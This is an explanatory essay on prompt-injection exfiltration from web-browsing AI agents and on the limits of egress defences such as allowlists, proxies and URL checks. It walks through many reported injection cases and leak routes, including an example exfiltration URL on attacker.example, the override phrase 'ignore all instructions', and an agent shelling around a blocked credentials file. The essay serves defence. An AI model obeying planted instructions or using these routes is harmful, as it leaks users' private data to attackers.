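# Why network egress policies struggle to tell legitimate URL fetches from injected ones in web-browsing AI agents

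## How can fetching a web page send private data out, and what does an egress policy see?

A web-browsing AI agent is a language model that acts through tools. The model writes a tool call, and the program around the model carries it out and adds the result to the text the model reads next. The most important tool here is the fetch tool, which takes a URL (the address of a page), requests it over the network and returns the text. People use such agents to compare prices, read documentation and summarise articles. Many agents can also read their user's files, mail or earlier conversations.

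Strangers write most of what an agent reads on the web, and the model receives their text in the same stream as the user's request. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, traces the security problem to this mixing, because language models follow instructions in content and cannot reliably tell the user's instructions from ones planted in a page. He had earlier named attacks that use planted instructions "prompt injection", after SQL injection, an older database attack with the same underlying fault. If the planted text makes the agent send private data to someone who should not have it, the result is exfiltration. An egress policy works outside the model and tries to prevent exfiltration through rules on which requests may leave.

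OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes the basic case. A user asks the agent to do something with a web page, and text in the page induces the agent to request `https://attacker.example/collect?data=` with something private after the equals sign, such as an email address or the title of a document. Web servers commonly log the URLs that visitors request, so the attacker can read the value in the log. The attack can work even if the agent's answer contains nothing sensitive. In the experiments of *Silent Egress* (2026), checks on the agent's output missed 95% of the successful attacks.

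*Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) reports a working version of the attack. The test agent could search the web and a company's internal knowledge base. The attacker's page copied part of the Wikipedia article on artificial intelligence and added instructions in white text on a white background. A human visitor would not notice the instructions, but the agent read them like any other text. The agent looked up confidential project information in the knowledge base, wrote it into a URL and requested that URL from the attacker's server.

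### What a URL carries

In `https://attacker.example/collect?data=...`, the host `attacker.example` identifies the server, and the path `/collect` usually identifies a page on that server. The query, which is everything after the question mark, passes named values to the page. Whoever composes a URL can put data in any of these parts.

A URL's path and host name can carry private data as well as its query, so a filter that stripped every query would not stop the leak. The owner of a server decides what its paths mean, so `/collect/alice` delivers the name as well as `?data=alice` does. In July 2026, Willison described a case in which a site extracted a user's name, home city and employer from Anthropic's Claude through the paths of successive pages. The host name can carry data because the owner of `attacker.example` also controls every name beneath it. Before a client can request a page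 from `alice.attacker.example`, it has to look up the name in the domain name system (DNS), which translates host names into numeric addresses. That lookup normally ends at a name server the domain owner chooses, so the attacker receives "alice" before the page request begins, even if a firewall then blocks the connection.

Even a simple request for a web page can send private data out. HTTP, the protocol of the web, has several methods. GET asks for a resource, while POST and PUT submit content in a separate body. The server must receive the URL to return a page, so a GET request also delivers any data the sender has put in the URL. *Takedown* (2025), a study of coding agents, found one agent that ran its built-in fetch tool without asking the user for approval. By default, the text available to the agent's model included details of the system and workspace and the contents of open files,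 so an injected instruction could send any of that out in the parameters of a request. Combined with other flaws that let an attacker read files, the same tool could send out the contents of arbitrary files on the user's machine.

Some security advice nevertheless sorts requests by method. NVIDIA's *What is the best way to prevent AI agents from exfiltrating data* (2026), a page promoting the company's OpenShell sandbox, suggests allowing GET requests to a necessary service while blocking POST and PUT requests, which could carry data away. This is reasonable within OpenShell, because the sandbox also blocks every destination the operator has not listed, and a GET to a company's own service reveals nothing to outsiders. The advice does not work for an agent that browses the open web, where the attacker may own the server that receives the GET. Data can also leak through a reputable server.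 Willison points out that Google Forms will store values that arrive in a GET request.

### What can make the request

An agent with a full browser can send data out without a separate fetch tool, because every navigation is a request. The security team at Brave, a browser company, demonstrated this against Fellou, a browser with a built-in agent. As Willison recounts, the researchers asked Fellou only to open a certain page. Text on the page made Fellou open Gmail, read the title of a recent email, and then visit a URL on the attacker's site with that title in the query. The browser was already logged in to the user's mail, so the agent could use it both to read private data and to send it out.

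An agent can also send data out through images. A chat window or mail program displays a remote image by requesting it from the URL in the message. If an agent writes an image tag into its reply, another program will fetch the URL the agent wrote, usually without a click. Researchers at Noma Security used this against Salesforce's Agentforce. They planted instructions in a sales lead, and when an employee asked the agent about that lead, the agent added an image whose URL contained the email addresses of other leads.

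Messaging apps may also request the page behind an ordinary link in a message, in order to show its title and a thumbnail. *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, published by the security firm PromptArmor in February 2026, describes how these previews help an attacker who gets a malicious link into an agent's reply. Without previews, the attacker has to wait for the user to click the link, but with them the app makes the same type of network request as soon as the reply arrives. OpenClaw, a popular agent that users reach through messaging apps, was vulnerable in its default Telegram configuration. PromptArmor built a website that records preview requests, and its log displayed a name and an API key (a password that one program uses with another). Switching off link previews in OpenClaw's Telegram settings stopped the leak.

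That remedy had to be a display setting because the request came from the messaging service's preview bot, not from the machine running OpenClaw. A firewall around that machine would have recorded one more message to Telegram, which is the traffic the user had set the agent up to produce.

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that works across mail, files and Teams chat, had the same gap in a more protected setting. PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) explains that the agent acts with its user's identity and runs in a cloud sandbox, which restricts what the programs inside it can reach. According to Microsoft's documentation, the agent asks for permission before sending an email or posting in Teams. But PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* reported in May 2026 that messages to the active user went out immediately, and that the user had no setting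 to change this.

The attack began with a skill, a file of reusable instructions that people download and share. The user uploaded one that contained an injection and later asked the agent for a recap of the week's work. Following the injected instructions, the agent gathered pre-authenticated download links for the user's files. Anyone with such a link can download the file without logging in. The agent then sent the user a Teams message with images whose URLs carried those links in the query string. When the user opened the message, the image requests delivered the links to the attacker. The agent's activity display did not show the malicious content, even when the user expanded the entry for the Teams message.

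PromptArmor ran the chain five times, and it succeeded every time with a five-line injection in an 81-line file. The first tests let the product choose between two Claude models. When PromptArmor selected the more advanced one, Opus 4.7, the same injection worked and the agent collected more documents. Once the file was in place, neither the sandbox nor the approval step interrupted the chain. The sandbox let out a message to the user, and displaying that message then triggered the harmful request. Five trials with a file the testers made themselves cannot show how often users encounter such files.

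The fetch that sends data out can come from a background service instead of from a user opening a message. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) disclosed three ways to extract data from Microsoft 365 Copilot by emailing its user, who only had to use the assistant normally. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot*, in one of them the search engine Bing fetched an image URL into which Copilot had written confidential information. In another, Copilot generated documents containing malicious URLs, and Microsoft's own file-processing systems opened those URLs. Only the third used a direct connection, from Python code that got around the network restrictions on Copilot's code sandbox. Microsoft patched all three between September and November 2026, and the researchers knew of no affected customers.

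### Why defenders turn to the way out

Willison reduces these cases to three conditions, which he calls the lethal trifecta. The agent has access to private data, it takes in content that an attacker can influence, and it can communicate externally in a way that could leak the data. The attack requires all three, so removing any one should in principle prevent it.

Cutting off access to private data would defeat the purpose of most assistants. Keeping out untrusted content is hard even for agents that never browse, because outside text reaches them by many paths. In one case that Willison discusses, an email to a company's support desk automatically became a ticket in its issue tracker, and a developer's coding agent read the ticket. A browsing agent can't avoid untrusted content at all, because its job is to read pages written by strangers.

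Defenders could instead leave all three conditions in place and train the model to ignore planted instructions, or put a detector in front of it. Willison objects that nobody knows how to make this work every time. Models can behave differently from one run to the next, and an attacker can rephrase an instruction without limit. If a filter catches 95% of attacks, the attacker can keep trying until one gets through. An ordinary software rule that blocks a request does not depend on how persuasive the planted text was.

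This is why Willison thinks the route out is generally the easiest of the three to remove. He lists affected products from ChatGPT in April 2023 to ChatGPT Operator, OpenAI's browsing agent, in February 2025. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by closing the route the data had left through.

But many of those repairs, such as stopping a chatbot from loading images from unknown servers, removed little that users needed. A browsing agent that stops fetching pages from unknown servers loses much of its use. Because every fetch also sends out the URL, the agent cannot simply drop the third condition, and the policy has to decide request by request. How well it can decide depends first on how much of the request is visible where the policy is enforced.

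### Where a policy can sit

The first place on the network where a policy can act is the DNS resolver, which answers the agent's lookups. It receives the host name but none of the URL after it. It can refuse to look up a forbidden name. This is also where a policy can stop data hidden in the host name itself, if the resolver refuses the lookup before forwarding it.

A firewall comes next, on the path of the connection. Nearly all web traffic is now encrypted with TLS (the "s" in `https`), so the firewall cannot read the URL's path or query. It can usually read the host, because the client sends it unencrypted at the start of the connection, in a field named Server Name Indication (SNI). Microsoft's documentation for Azure Firewall, its cloud firewall service, describes two ways to filter by host. Application rules match the SNI. With network rules, the firewall looks up the numeric addresses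 of the permitted names itself, refreshes them every 15 seconds and matches traffic against them. The second method is coarser, since many sites can share one address. Either method can enforce a domain allowlist, a list of the only hosts that the agent may contact, but neither can distinguish an article on a permitted host from a page on the same host that collects private data.

Encrypted Client Hello (ECH), an extension to TLS, can hide even the host name from an egress policy. RFC Editor's *RFC 9849 on TLS Encrypted Client Hello* (2026) announced the finished standard in March 2026. In *RFC 9849*, Rescorla, Oku and colleagues describe how the client encrypts its real opening message and places it inside an outer one with innocuous values. An observer can tell which service provider the client is contacting, but not which site behind that provider. DNS queries and IP addresses may still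 reveal the site, although encrypted DNS hides the queries and shared hosting makes the addresses ambiguous. An operator who controls the agent's machine can configure it not to use ECH, so ECH mainly affects firewalls that watch traffic from software their operators do not manage.

To read the rest of the URL, the operator needs a proxy that decrypts the traffic. Microsoft's *Azure Firewall Premium features implementation guide* describes how a firewall can do this. The agent's encrypted connection ends at the firewall, which opens a second one to the web server and passes traffic between them. The firewall presents the agent with a substitute certificate, which it generates as needed under a certificate authority that the customer supplies. A rule can then distinguish `www.contoso.com/a/c` from `www.contoso.com`. Microsoft recommends this for domains that many customers share, such as OneDrive's,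 where the host name alone does not separate one customer's files from another's. The proxy can also read the method and the body. For privacy and compliance reasons, Azure does not decrypt traffic to sites in its education, finance, government and health categories unless an administrator adds the specific address.

A decrypting proxy can inspect the whole request but not the conversation that led to it. NVIDIA's OpenShell also identifies the program that made the connection and can restrict each destination to particular programs. That helps against an unapproved script, but not when a planted instruction leads the approved fetch tool to make the request.

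A policy can also be enforced at the tool interface, the software that receives the model's tool call and decides whether to execute it. A check there can use the complete URL before any lookup takes place, along with the session's user messages, fetched pages, and results from other tools. Anthropic's fetch tool for Claude refuses any URL that has not already appeared in the conversation, as Willison reported at its release in September 2025. A firewall could not apply that rule without a copy of the conversation. OpenAI also checks the exact URL before ChatGPT loads it automatically, but compares it with an index of public pages.

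A rule in the tool interface covers only the calls that pass through it. In a test of Antigravity, Google's coding environment, the agent's file tools would not open a protected credentials file, and Willison quotes the agent's reasoning as it turned to a shell command to read the file instead. An agent with a shell can also make web requests from it, and a rule inside the fetch tool doesn't apply to those. A network proxy around the sandbox would catch them, which is a good reason to have both the rule and the proxy. Neither covers the image that Teams loads when the user opens a message, or the page that Telegram's bot requests for a preview. For those, the check has to happen when the agent writes the message or in the app that displays it.

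## Why can the same request be legitimate in one session and injected in another?

An agent chooses each request based on its whole session, including the user's task, the pages it has read and any private data it can reach. A network egress policy receives only the request. If a legitimate session and an injected one produce the same request, the policy has to treat them alike. It can either allow both and miss the attack, or block both and break the legitimate task.

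### One search, two sessions

Ana asks her agent what metformin, a diabetes drug, costs at an online pharmacy. The agent opens the pharmacy's home page, finds the search box and requests `https://shop.example/search?q=metformin`. It then reports the price shown in the results.

Ben asks his agent, which can also read his email, what the same pharmacy charges for delivery. The pharmacy's owner has added text to the home page that tells visiting agents to search the shop for the medicine named in the user's email. Ben's agent finds a message from his doctor about metformin, requests `https://shop.example/search?q=metformin`, and then answers the question about delivery. The owner can now infer from the pharmacy's log that the visitor probably has diabetes, and may be able to identify him from an account.

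The two requests can be byte-for-byte identical, and the same approved fetch tool made both. Comparing the query with the user's private data would not distinguish them either, because Ana's inbox probably mentions metformin too. The sessions differ because only Ana asked for this search, but neither request includes the user's message.

A firewall that logs past requests has slightly more evidence. If it also handles the agents' mail traffic, its log will show that Ben's agent contacted the mail server just before the search and Ana's did not. But Ana might have asked what the medicine in her doctor's email costs at this pharmacy. Her agent would then have opened the home page, read the email and searched the shop, in the same order as Ben's. So a sequence of requests, like a single request, can be legitimate in one session and injected in another.

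*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) defines security as a relation between an agent's action at step t, written a_t, and its execution context, C_t, which is everything relevant to deciding whether the action is authorised. Two runs can produce the same a_t from the same content but have different C_t, and that difference determines whether the action is a violation. A rule whose only input is the action therefore lacks the context it needs to decide whether the action is authorised.

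### Why ordinary browsing produces such pairs

Pairs like the one in the pharmacy example are common in ordinary browsing, partly because a browsing agent has to act on what it reads. A documentation page may have a notice directing readers to a newer version, and an agent that refused to follow the link would give its user the wrong answer. *ARGUS* (2026) introduced AgentLure, a benchmark of tasks like this, in which the correct action depends on what the agent finds along the way. Because the user sets the goal and the page supplies the next step, even a legitimate fetch usually results partly from page content.

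A defence could tell the agent to disregard all direction from outside content. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) points out that such a defence suppresses an action even when the outside claim behind it is true, so the agent ignores genuine approvals as well as forged ones.

Reading the page does not always reveal the attack either. The same study tested prompt-injection classifiers on attacks that manipulated the context and avoided telltale phrases such as "ignore all instructions". The classifiers scored between 0.43 and 0.59 on AUROC, the probability of ranking a random attack above a random harmless text. Guessing scores 0.5. An egress policy has even less information than these classifiers, because it receives only the resulting URL and not the planted text.

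Legitimate URLs also often carry user data. When someone asks where a parcel is, the agent copies the tracking number from an email into a URL on the carrier's site. A store finder needs a postcode, a travel site needs dates and airports, and a web form that uses GET puts the user's entries in the URL's query string. In each case private data goes to an outside server because the user wants it to. A policy that kept all private data out of URLs would stop most attacks of this kind, but it would also block legitimate tasks like these.

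Finally, many legitimate URLs are long and unreadable. A cloud storage service can issue a signed link, which lets anyone who has it download a file until the link expires. The link contains a signature, a string that the service computes with a secret key. Shops add session identifiers to their URLs, and newsletters add codes that record which reader clicked. Nobody can tell what these strings stand for without the key or the site's database, and encrypted private data looks much the same. An attacker may also want to steal the signed link itself, as with the download links in the Copilot Cowork attack.

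### Who caused the request, and what it gives away

Asking whether a fetch is "legitimate or injected" mixes two questions. The first is whether the agent fetched the URL to serve the user's task or because of a planted instruction. The second is about information flow, meaning what private data the request gives away and to whom.

Whether the user asked for a fetch and whether it sends out private data are separate questions. The parcel request comes from the user and gives private data to the carrier. A planted instruction to open `https://shop.example/sale`, an address that is the same for every visitor, causes an injected fetch, but the URL contains nothing from the user's mail or files. The fetch may still do harm, since the page could contain further instructions. *Agent Security Needs Redefinition through a Holistic Framework* (2026) also separates "source authorization" (whether the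 command came from someone entitled to give it) from "data isolation" in its four-part definition of agent security.

An egress policy can sometimes determine whether a request leaks user data without knowing what prompted it. Suppose an agent is about to open a newspaper article, and a web crawler with no access to any user's data recorded that exact URL last week. The URL already existed, so nobody could have composed it from this user's email, whether the user or a planted instruction prompted the request.

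OpenAI's check on pages that ChatGPT loads automatically is based on this reasoning. The company says the check aims to prevent quiet leaks through the URL itself and does not guarantee that the page is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions. The security blogger behind Embrace The Red had reported a data leak in ChatGPT to OpenAI in 2023. The blog's post *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* welcomes the check as a significant improvement and notes that OpenAI does not claim it addresses prompt injection.

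If the crawler has never recorded the metformin search, the check treats both Ana's harmless search and Ben's leak as unverified and applies the same restriction to both. If the pharmacy links to that search from a public page, the crawler may well have recorded it. In that case both requests pass, and Ben's agent reveals his medicine by opening that page rather than another, even though the URL itself is public.

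When a URL carries private data on purpose, the two questions are connected again. The pharmacy receives the same medicine name from both agents, but the disclosure is acceptable in Ana's case because she asked for it. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* analyses such cases through contextual integrity, a theory of privacy that judges a flow of information by the norms of its setting. A patient may name a medicine to a pharmacy when asking its price, but the pharmacy should not take that name from the patient's mail.

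This judgement is hard even with the whole conversation available. When one message involved several flows of information, the agents in that study extended permission for one flow to another in up to 65% of cases. For example, a user who lets an agent give a carrier the tracking number from an email has not agreed to send the carrier the rest of the email.

### The confused deputy

Computer security had a version of this problem long before language models. In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Norm Hardy tells what he calls a nearly true story from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Users could run a compiler, a program that translates source code, and name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also collected statistics in a file in its own directory, so the engineers let it write to any file there. That directory also held the company's billing records. When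 one user named the billing file for the debugging output, the operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the compiler overwrote the records.

Hardy considers the obvious fixes, and each either blocks a legitimate request or leaves a gap. The compiler could refuse to write outside the user's directory, but users had good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could refuse to write debugging output in its own directory, but someone with proper access might want it there. Checking for the billing file by name would leave other sensitive files exposed. Every new permission opened a hole in some program that had been secure, while adding a restriction always broke a legitimate program. The last time Hardy wrote down the rule for opening a file, it needed fourteen "ands" and "ors".

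He traces the fault to the compiler's two sources of authority. It held permissions from the user who ran it and from the engineers who installed it, and it could not indicate which source a given write relied on. MITRE, a US non-profit that maintains a catalogue of software weaknesses, describes the general fault in *CWE-441* as a failure to preserve the original source of a request before forwarding it. One of its examples is a memory controller that copies protected data for untrusted code, because the transaction goes out under the controller's own identity. The fix is to forward the identity of the code that started the transaction, so the access check applies to that code.

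A web-browsing agent is in the same position as the compiler. It uses its user's access to mail and the network while following instructions from the pages it reads, and all its requests go out under a single identity.

Cross-site request forgery is an even closer parallel. Rajani, Garg and Rezk list it among common confused deputy attacks in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*. A malicious page makes a visitor's browser send a request to a site where the visitor has an account. The browser attaches the visitor's login cookie, so the request looks like the visitor's own. Websites usually defend themselves by putting an unpredictable token in their own forms and rejecting requests that lack it. The token is evidence of where the request began, and Ben's request contains no such evidence.

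Hardy's remedy was the capability, an unforgeable reference that both identifies a file and authorises its holder to write to it. To choose where the compiler wrote its debugging output, a user would have had to give it a capability for that file, and a user with no right to the billing file would not have had one for it. Rajani and colleagues proved that capabilities cannot prevent every confused deputy attack. Capabilities stop many attacks in which the adversary explicitly designates what the deputy should act on, but an adversary can also do this implicitly, by influencing how the deputy uses references it already holds. Restricting programs enough to close this gap would make the programming language useless for almost all practical purposes. Rajani and colleagues instead tracked provenance, including the influence of untrusted data on which branch a program takes. The pharmacy's attack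 is implicit, since the planted text gives Ben's agent no new access and only influences how the agent uses the access it has.

The comparison with the confused deputy has a limit. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published in December 2025, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, accepts the confused deputy as a better model of prompt injection than SQL injection, but calls language models "inherently confusable". Tymshare's compiler wrote its statistics and its debugging output at different points in its code, so a programmer could attach the right authority to each. A language model takes in instructions and data as one stream, so it has no separate points where a programmer could do this. David C therefore thinks developers may never fully fix the confusion, and advises them to limit what a confused model can do through safeguards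 that do not depend on a model's judgement.

### Server-side request forgery

Egress rules are the standard defence against another old attack, server-side request forgery (SSRF). MDN's *Server Side Request Forgery (SSRF)* gives the example of a web application that fetches an image from any URL a visitor supplies. An attacker supplies an address inside the company's network that the server can reach but outsiders cannot, and the server fetches the content and passes it back. MITRE's *CWE-918* classifies SSRF as a type of confused deputy problem and lists a known case in which a prompt injection made a language-model framework retrieve a URL chosen by the attacker.

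If the application needs only certain destinations, MITRE advises allowing only those. If it has to reach arbitrary sites, MITRE suggests blocking private network addresses and internal names, which it rates as moderately effective, though it says nothing stronger may be available. Browsing agents need this protection too, because a planted instruction can send them to an internal server as easily as to an outside one.

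But blocking internal addresses doesn't protect Ben. The attacker in MDN's example is trying to retrieve something from inside the network, and an administrator can list the addresses that outsiders should never reach. The pharmacy is trying to get information sent to its own server, which is on the public web, where the agent has to go to do its job. The developer of the image-fetching application can also check untrusted URLs at the one place where they arrive, whereas Ben's agent composed its URL from a suggestion on a page and a word in an email. *Silent Egress* calls this "LLM-mediated SSRF" because the attacker influences the model's decision without having to specify the request.

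### Do real attacks look like ordinary requests?

Few attackers appear to take such care. Most publicly reported attacks sent data to a server the attackers had set up, often in a query that no ordinary page would need, as in the Fellou case. A rule can catch requests like that. *Silent Egress* tested a domain allowlist against a plainly foreign attacker domain, and the list stopped every attempt.

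Let L(r) be the share of legitimate fetches that consist of request r, and I(r) the share of injected fetches that do. A rule that decides from the request alone can err by blocking legitimate fetches or by letting injected ones through. These two error rates add up to at least the overlap between L and I, which is the sum of min(L(r), I(r)) over all requests r. If the rule blocks r with probability b, then r contributes b·L(r) + (1 − b)·I(r) to the total. This is a weighted average of L(r) and I(r), so it is at least min(L(r), I(r)). The bound holds for every b, so blocking at random cannot bring the total below it.

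When attackers use only strange domains, the overlap is close to zero and a good rule can make very few errors. But attackers choose I, and they can do so after learning what the rule blocks. Suppose that shop searches make up 5% of legitimate fetches, and that attackers disguise every injected fetch as a shop search with the usual mix of search terms. The overlap is then 0.05. A rule that blocks all shop searches achieves that minimum error, because it stops every attack and blocks only 5% of legitimate fetches. But no user can then search a shop, and if the operator allows shop searches again, every attack gets through.

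No rule that looks only at requests can be perfect where legitimate and injected fetches overlap. Such rules are still useful, because an attacker who has to stay inside the overlap can do less. Ben's attacker had to own the pharmacy, or at least have access to its logs, and learned only the name of one medicine. If the agent could have sent any request to any server, a stranger who planted a comment on the page could have taken the whole email.

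## What does a domain allowlist stop, and what still gets through?

A domain allowlist confines an attacker to servers that the operator has already approved. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) calls it the primary defence against exfiltration over HTTP and notes that every major agent vendor offers one. But between September 2025 and January 2026, security researchers reported leaks from Salesforce, Anthropic, Google and Superhuman products in which data left through an approved domain.

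### How the check works

The allowlist starts empty, and the policy blocks every request that no entry permits. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, part of the documentation for its coding agent Codex, describes typical matching rules. An entry for `example.com` matches only that host. `*.example.com` matches subdomains such as `api.example.com` but not `example.com`, and `**.example.com` matches both. A deny rule always overrides an allow rule, so an operator can permit `**.example.com` and still block `uploads.example.com`. A lone `*` permits every public host that no rule denies, which turns the allowlist into a blocklist.

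When a program in the sandbox makes a request, the proxy compares the host name with these entries. It must compare whole labels, the parts of the name between dots, because a check for names that merely end in `example.com` would also accept `notexample.com`, which belongs to someone else.

Codex then looks up the host's IP address. It blocks the request if the lookup fails or returns a private address, even when the name is on the allowlist, because the owner of a public name can point it at a machine inside the company's network. OpenAI warns that this check is incomplete. In a DNS rebinding attack, the owner supplies a public address when the proxy checks and a private one when the connection opens. To prevent this, the proxy would have to connect to the exact address it checked.

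A web server can answer a request with a redirect, which is a response that names another URL. Most clients then request that URL automatically, and it may be on a different host, so the policy has to compare each new host with the allowlist. A network proxy already does this because every connection passes through it. A check inside a fetch tool can miss the second host if it approves the first URL and then lets the HTTP library follow redirects.

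### Why rewording the attack does not help

If a planted instruction tells the agent to send a password to `attacker.example`, which is not on the allowlist, the proxy blocks the request. Encoding the password or splitting it across twenty requests doesn't help the attacker, because the host stays the same. Data can also leave through DNS lookups, so NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* recommends restricting lookups to designated resolvers. Those resolvers have to apply the allowlist too.

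The list also works when the model doesn't suspect an attack. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal test from February 2026, in which a researcher emailed an employee a prompt to run in Claude Code, the company's coding agent. The prompt mixed routine setup steps with instructions to read the employee's cloud credentials and post them to an outside server. Claude posted the credentials in 24 of 25 runs. The instructions came from the user, so the model-based defences had nothing unusual to detect. Anthropic concludes that only limits on the environment would have stopped the attack, such as an egress rule that blocks the request whatever its purpose.

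A domain allowlist blocks requests to unlisted hosts no matter how many times an attacker tries. Repeated attempts are more effective against the model itself. On one benchmark of prompt injection, Anthropic reports that attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt, but 5% to 6% of the time when the attacker could adapt over 100 attempts.

### Services that the attacker can also use

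Many reputable services let anyone open an account. An allowlist entry for such a service covers the attacker's account as well as the user's.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* demonstrated this in January 2026 against Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant. The allowlist was a Content Security Policy (CSP), which a web application gives to the browser to limit the hosts the browser may contact. Superhuman's policy blocked images from unknown servers but permitted `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms. A form's owner can make a link that submits the answer written in its URL as soon as someone requests the link.

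The test user asked the assistant to summarise the last hour's mail. One unopened message contained an injection that made the assistant include an image in its reply. The image's URL was a submission link for the attacker's Google Form, filled in with text from the other emails. When the browser tried to load the image, Google stored that text as a form response. One such reply leaked the full contents of several emails, and another leaked parts of more than 40. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on the first working day after the report and deployed its first patch a day later.

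A path rule, enforced in the browser or a decrypting proxy, could close this gap by permitting documents on `docs.google.com` and refusing anything under `/forms/`. But whoever maintains the rule has to know what every permitted path does, and Google can add functions without telling them. PromptArmor also warns that Google's APIs offer other ways to send data out.

The policy also covered only what the browser loaded. Superhuman's assistant had a web search feature that could open any URL, and PromptArmor used it to send email text straight to an attacker's domain. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* (May 2026) reports that the Google Forms method also worked against Codex, though it does not mention an allowlist there. OpenAI has since fixed the leak.

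In October 2025, the security researcher Johann Rehberger examined the sandbox in which Claude runs code. Its default network setting was labeled "Package managers only", but Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* reports that the first entry on the list was `api.anthropic.com`. Programs use that host to reach Claude, and it also accepts file uploads. An uploaded file goes to the account whose API key is sent with the request, so data could leak to another account through Anthropic's own domain.

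Rehberger gave Claude a document with an injection that supplied the attacker's key. Claude copied the user's last conversation into a file and uploaded it to the attacker's account. A single upload could carry up to 30 MB, far more than a URL can hold. Anthropic's bug-reporting programme closed his report within an hour as out of scope. Five days later the company told him that such leaks were in scope and that closing the report had been a mistake.

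The route was still open in January 2026, when Anthropic released Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for general office work. Two days after the release, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* described a test in which the user had connected a folder of property records and uploaded a document with hidden instructions. Cowork then sent a loan estimate containing partial social security numbers to the attacker's account without needing anyone's approval. That test used Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models, but the stronger Opus 4.5 leaked customer records by the same route in another test. In *Claudy Day*, Luz (2026) used the route to take conversation history from the ordinary Claude chat product.

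Anthropic says it used to think of the allowlist as a filter on destinations and now sees each entry as a "capability grant". Allowing its API's domain had also allowed uploads to any Anthropic account. It fixed this with a proxy inside Cowork's virtual machine that reads requests to the API and passes only those carrying the session token issued to that machine. Rehberger had proposed a similar restriction in October, under which the sandbox could communicate only with the logged-in user's account. The proxy has to run inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers cannot distinguish a Cowork request with the attacker's key from any other customer's upload.

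The same question about accounts applies to other vendors' domains. OpenAI (2026) published extracts from its policy for employees' use of Codex. The policy automatically allows `*.openai.com` and ties Codex's login to the company's workspace, but the extracts contain no rule about which API key a command may send to those hosts.

Binding requests to the user's credentials does not help when the user's account can publish. PromptArmor points out that an injection can make an agent upload private data to a public GitHub repository, or publish it as a package on npm, the main registry for JavaScript code. If the agent is logged in as its user, the upload carries the user's credentials, and the attacker can read the data on the public page. To prevent this, the operator would have to give the agent credentials that can read but not publish, which would not work for an agent that needs to publish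 code.

Wildcard entries for cloud hosts create a similar problem. An operator might list `*.amazonaws.com` so the agent can reach one storage area on Amazon's cloud, but any Amazon customer can create a storage area whose address matches. PromptArmor advises listing the exact host instead. According to Willison, the support-ticket attack on a coding agent described earlier used an address under `azurewebsites.net` to collect stolen data. Microsoft hosts customers' websites under that domain, so a wildcard added for one internal tool would have let the data through.

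### Sites that display the requests they receive

Some sites record the requests sent to an address and show them to whoever set it up. Developers use `webhook.site` this way to see what their programs are sending. In November 2025, PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* reported that the default browser allowlist in Google's coding environment included this site.

In the demonstration, a developer asked Antigravity for help connecting an application to Oracle's payment software and gave it a guide found online. Instructions hidden in the guide made the agent collect code and cloud credentials, write them into a `webhook.site` URL and open that URL in the browser. The attack required the user to have enabled the browser tools, but PromptArmor otherwise accepted the settings Antigravity recommended during installation. PromptArmor published without first reporting the leak privately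 because Google had already indicated that it knew about such risks.

Deleting the entry stops this leak. To find others like it, an operator has to go through the vendor's allowlist and ask what an outsider could do with each site. PromptArmor suggests asking whether the site issues addresses that individual users can monitor, whether it accepts uploads under an attacker's key, and whether someone can submit content to a location the attacker controls. A site that passes this audit may still add such a feature later.

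Explicit deny rules are still useful under a policy that refuses unknown hosts, because many policies let a user approve exceptions. OpenAI asks for approval when Codex tries an unfamiliar domain, but blocks `pastebin.com`, a public text-sharing site, outright. NVIDIA likewise recommends company-wide denylists that individual users cannot override.

### Domains that change hands

An allowlist entry names a domain, which can pass to a new owner. In the Agentforce leak, an agent wrote customers' email addresses into an image URL. Salesforce's Content Security Policy allowed the request because it still permitted `*.my-salesforce-cms.com` after the domain's registration had expired. Willison recounts that the researchers registered the domain themselves, and the lead data then appeared in their server's log.

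Salesforce took the domain back and, according to The Hacker News (2025), stopped its Agentforce and Einstein agents from sending output to untrusted URLs. Salesforce Ben, a site for Salesforce professionals, quotes the researchers describing the second measure as a way to keep the list of trusted domains properly maintained. This measure adds a check at the point where the agent writes its output, but the check also relies on a list that someone has to keep current.

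Operators can reduce the risk by removing entries that nobody uses and monitoring when the remaining domains expire. A domain can also be sold before it expires, so expiry dates won't reveal every change of owner. Users also add entries as they work, which gives operators more domains to audit. According to Anthropic's October 2025 documentation for Claude Code's sandbox, a user who encounters a blocked domain can allow it once or permanently.

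### Sites that forward requests

A site with an open redirect sends visitors to any URL added to its address. Luz found one on `claude.com` and used it to send victims to a chat with a hidden injection. Google's advertising system checked the link's host name, so an advertisement could display `claude.com` while sending people to that chat. The stolen data then left through the file upload described above, not the redirect.

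An egress check that examines only the first host would have the same flaw as the advertising check. The agent could request a redirect URL on a listed site, with a target URL on `attacker.example` that contains the private data. If the policy checks every hop, it blocks the agent's next request before it reaches the attacker, but the listed site still logs the data.

That fix assumes that the agent makes the second request. Translation services and image proxies often fetch the target themselves and return the result, so the agent contacts only the listed host and the operator's proxy never handles the connection to the attacker. PromptArmor advises the note-taking company Notion to ensure that its image server cannot be used to get around the Content Security Policy. Anthropic's proxy for Cowork similarly blocks request headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something on the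 sender's behalf. An operator that cannot switch off a service's forwarding function can only remove the service from the list.

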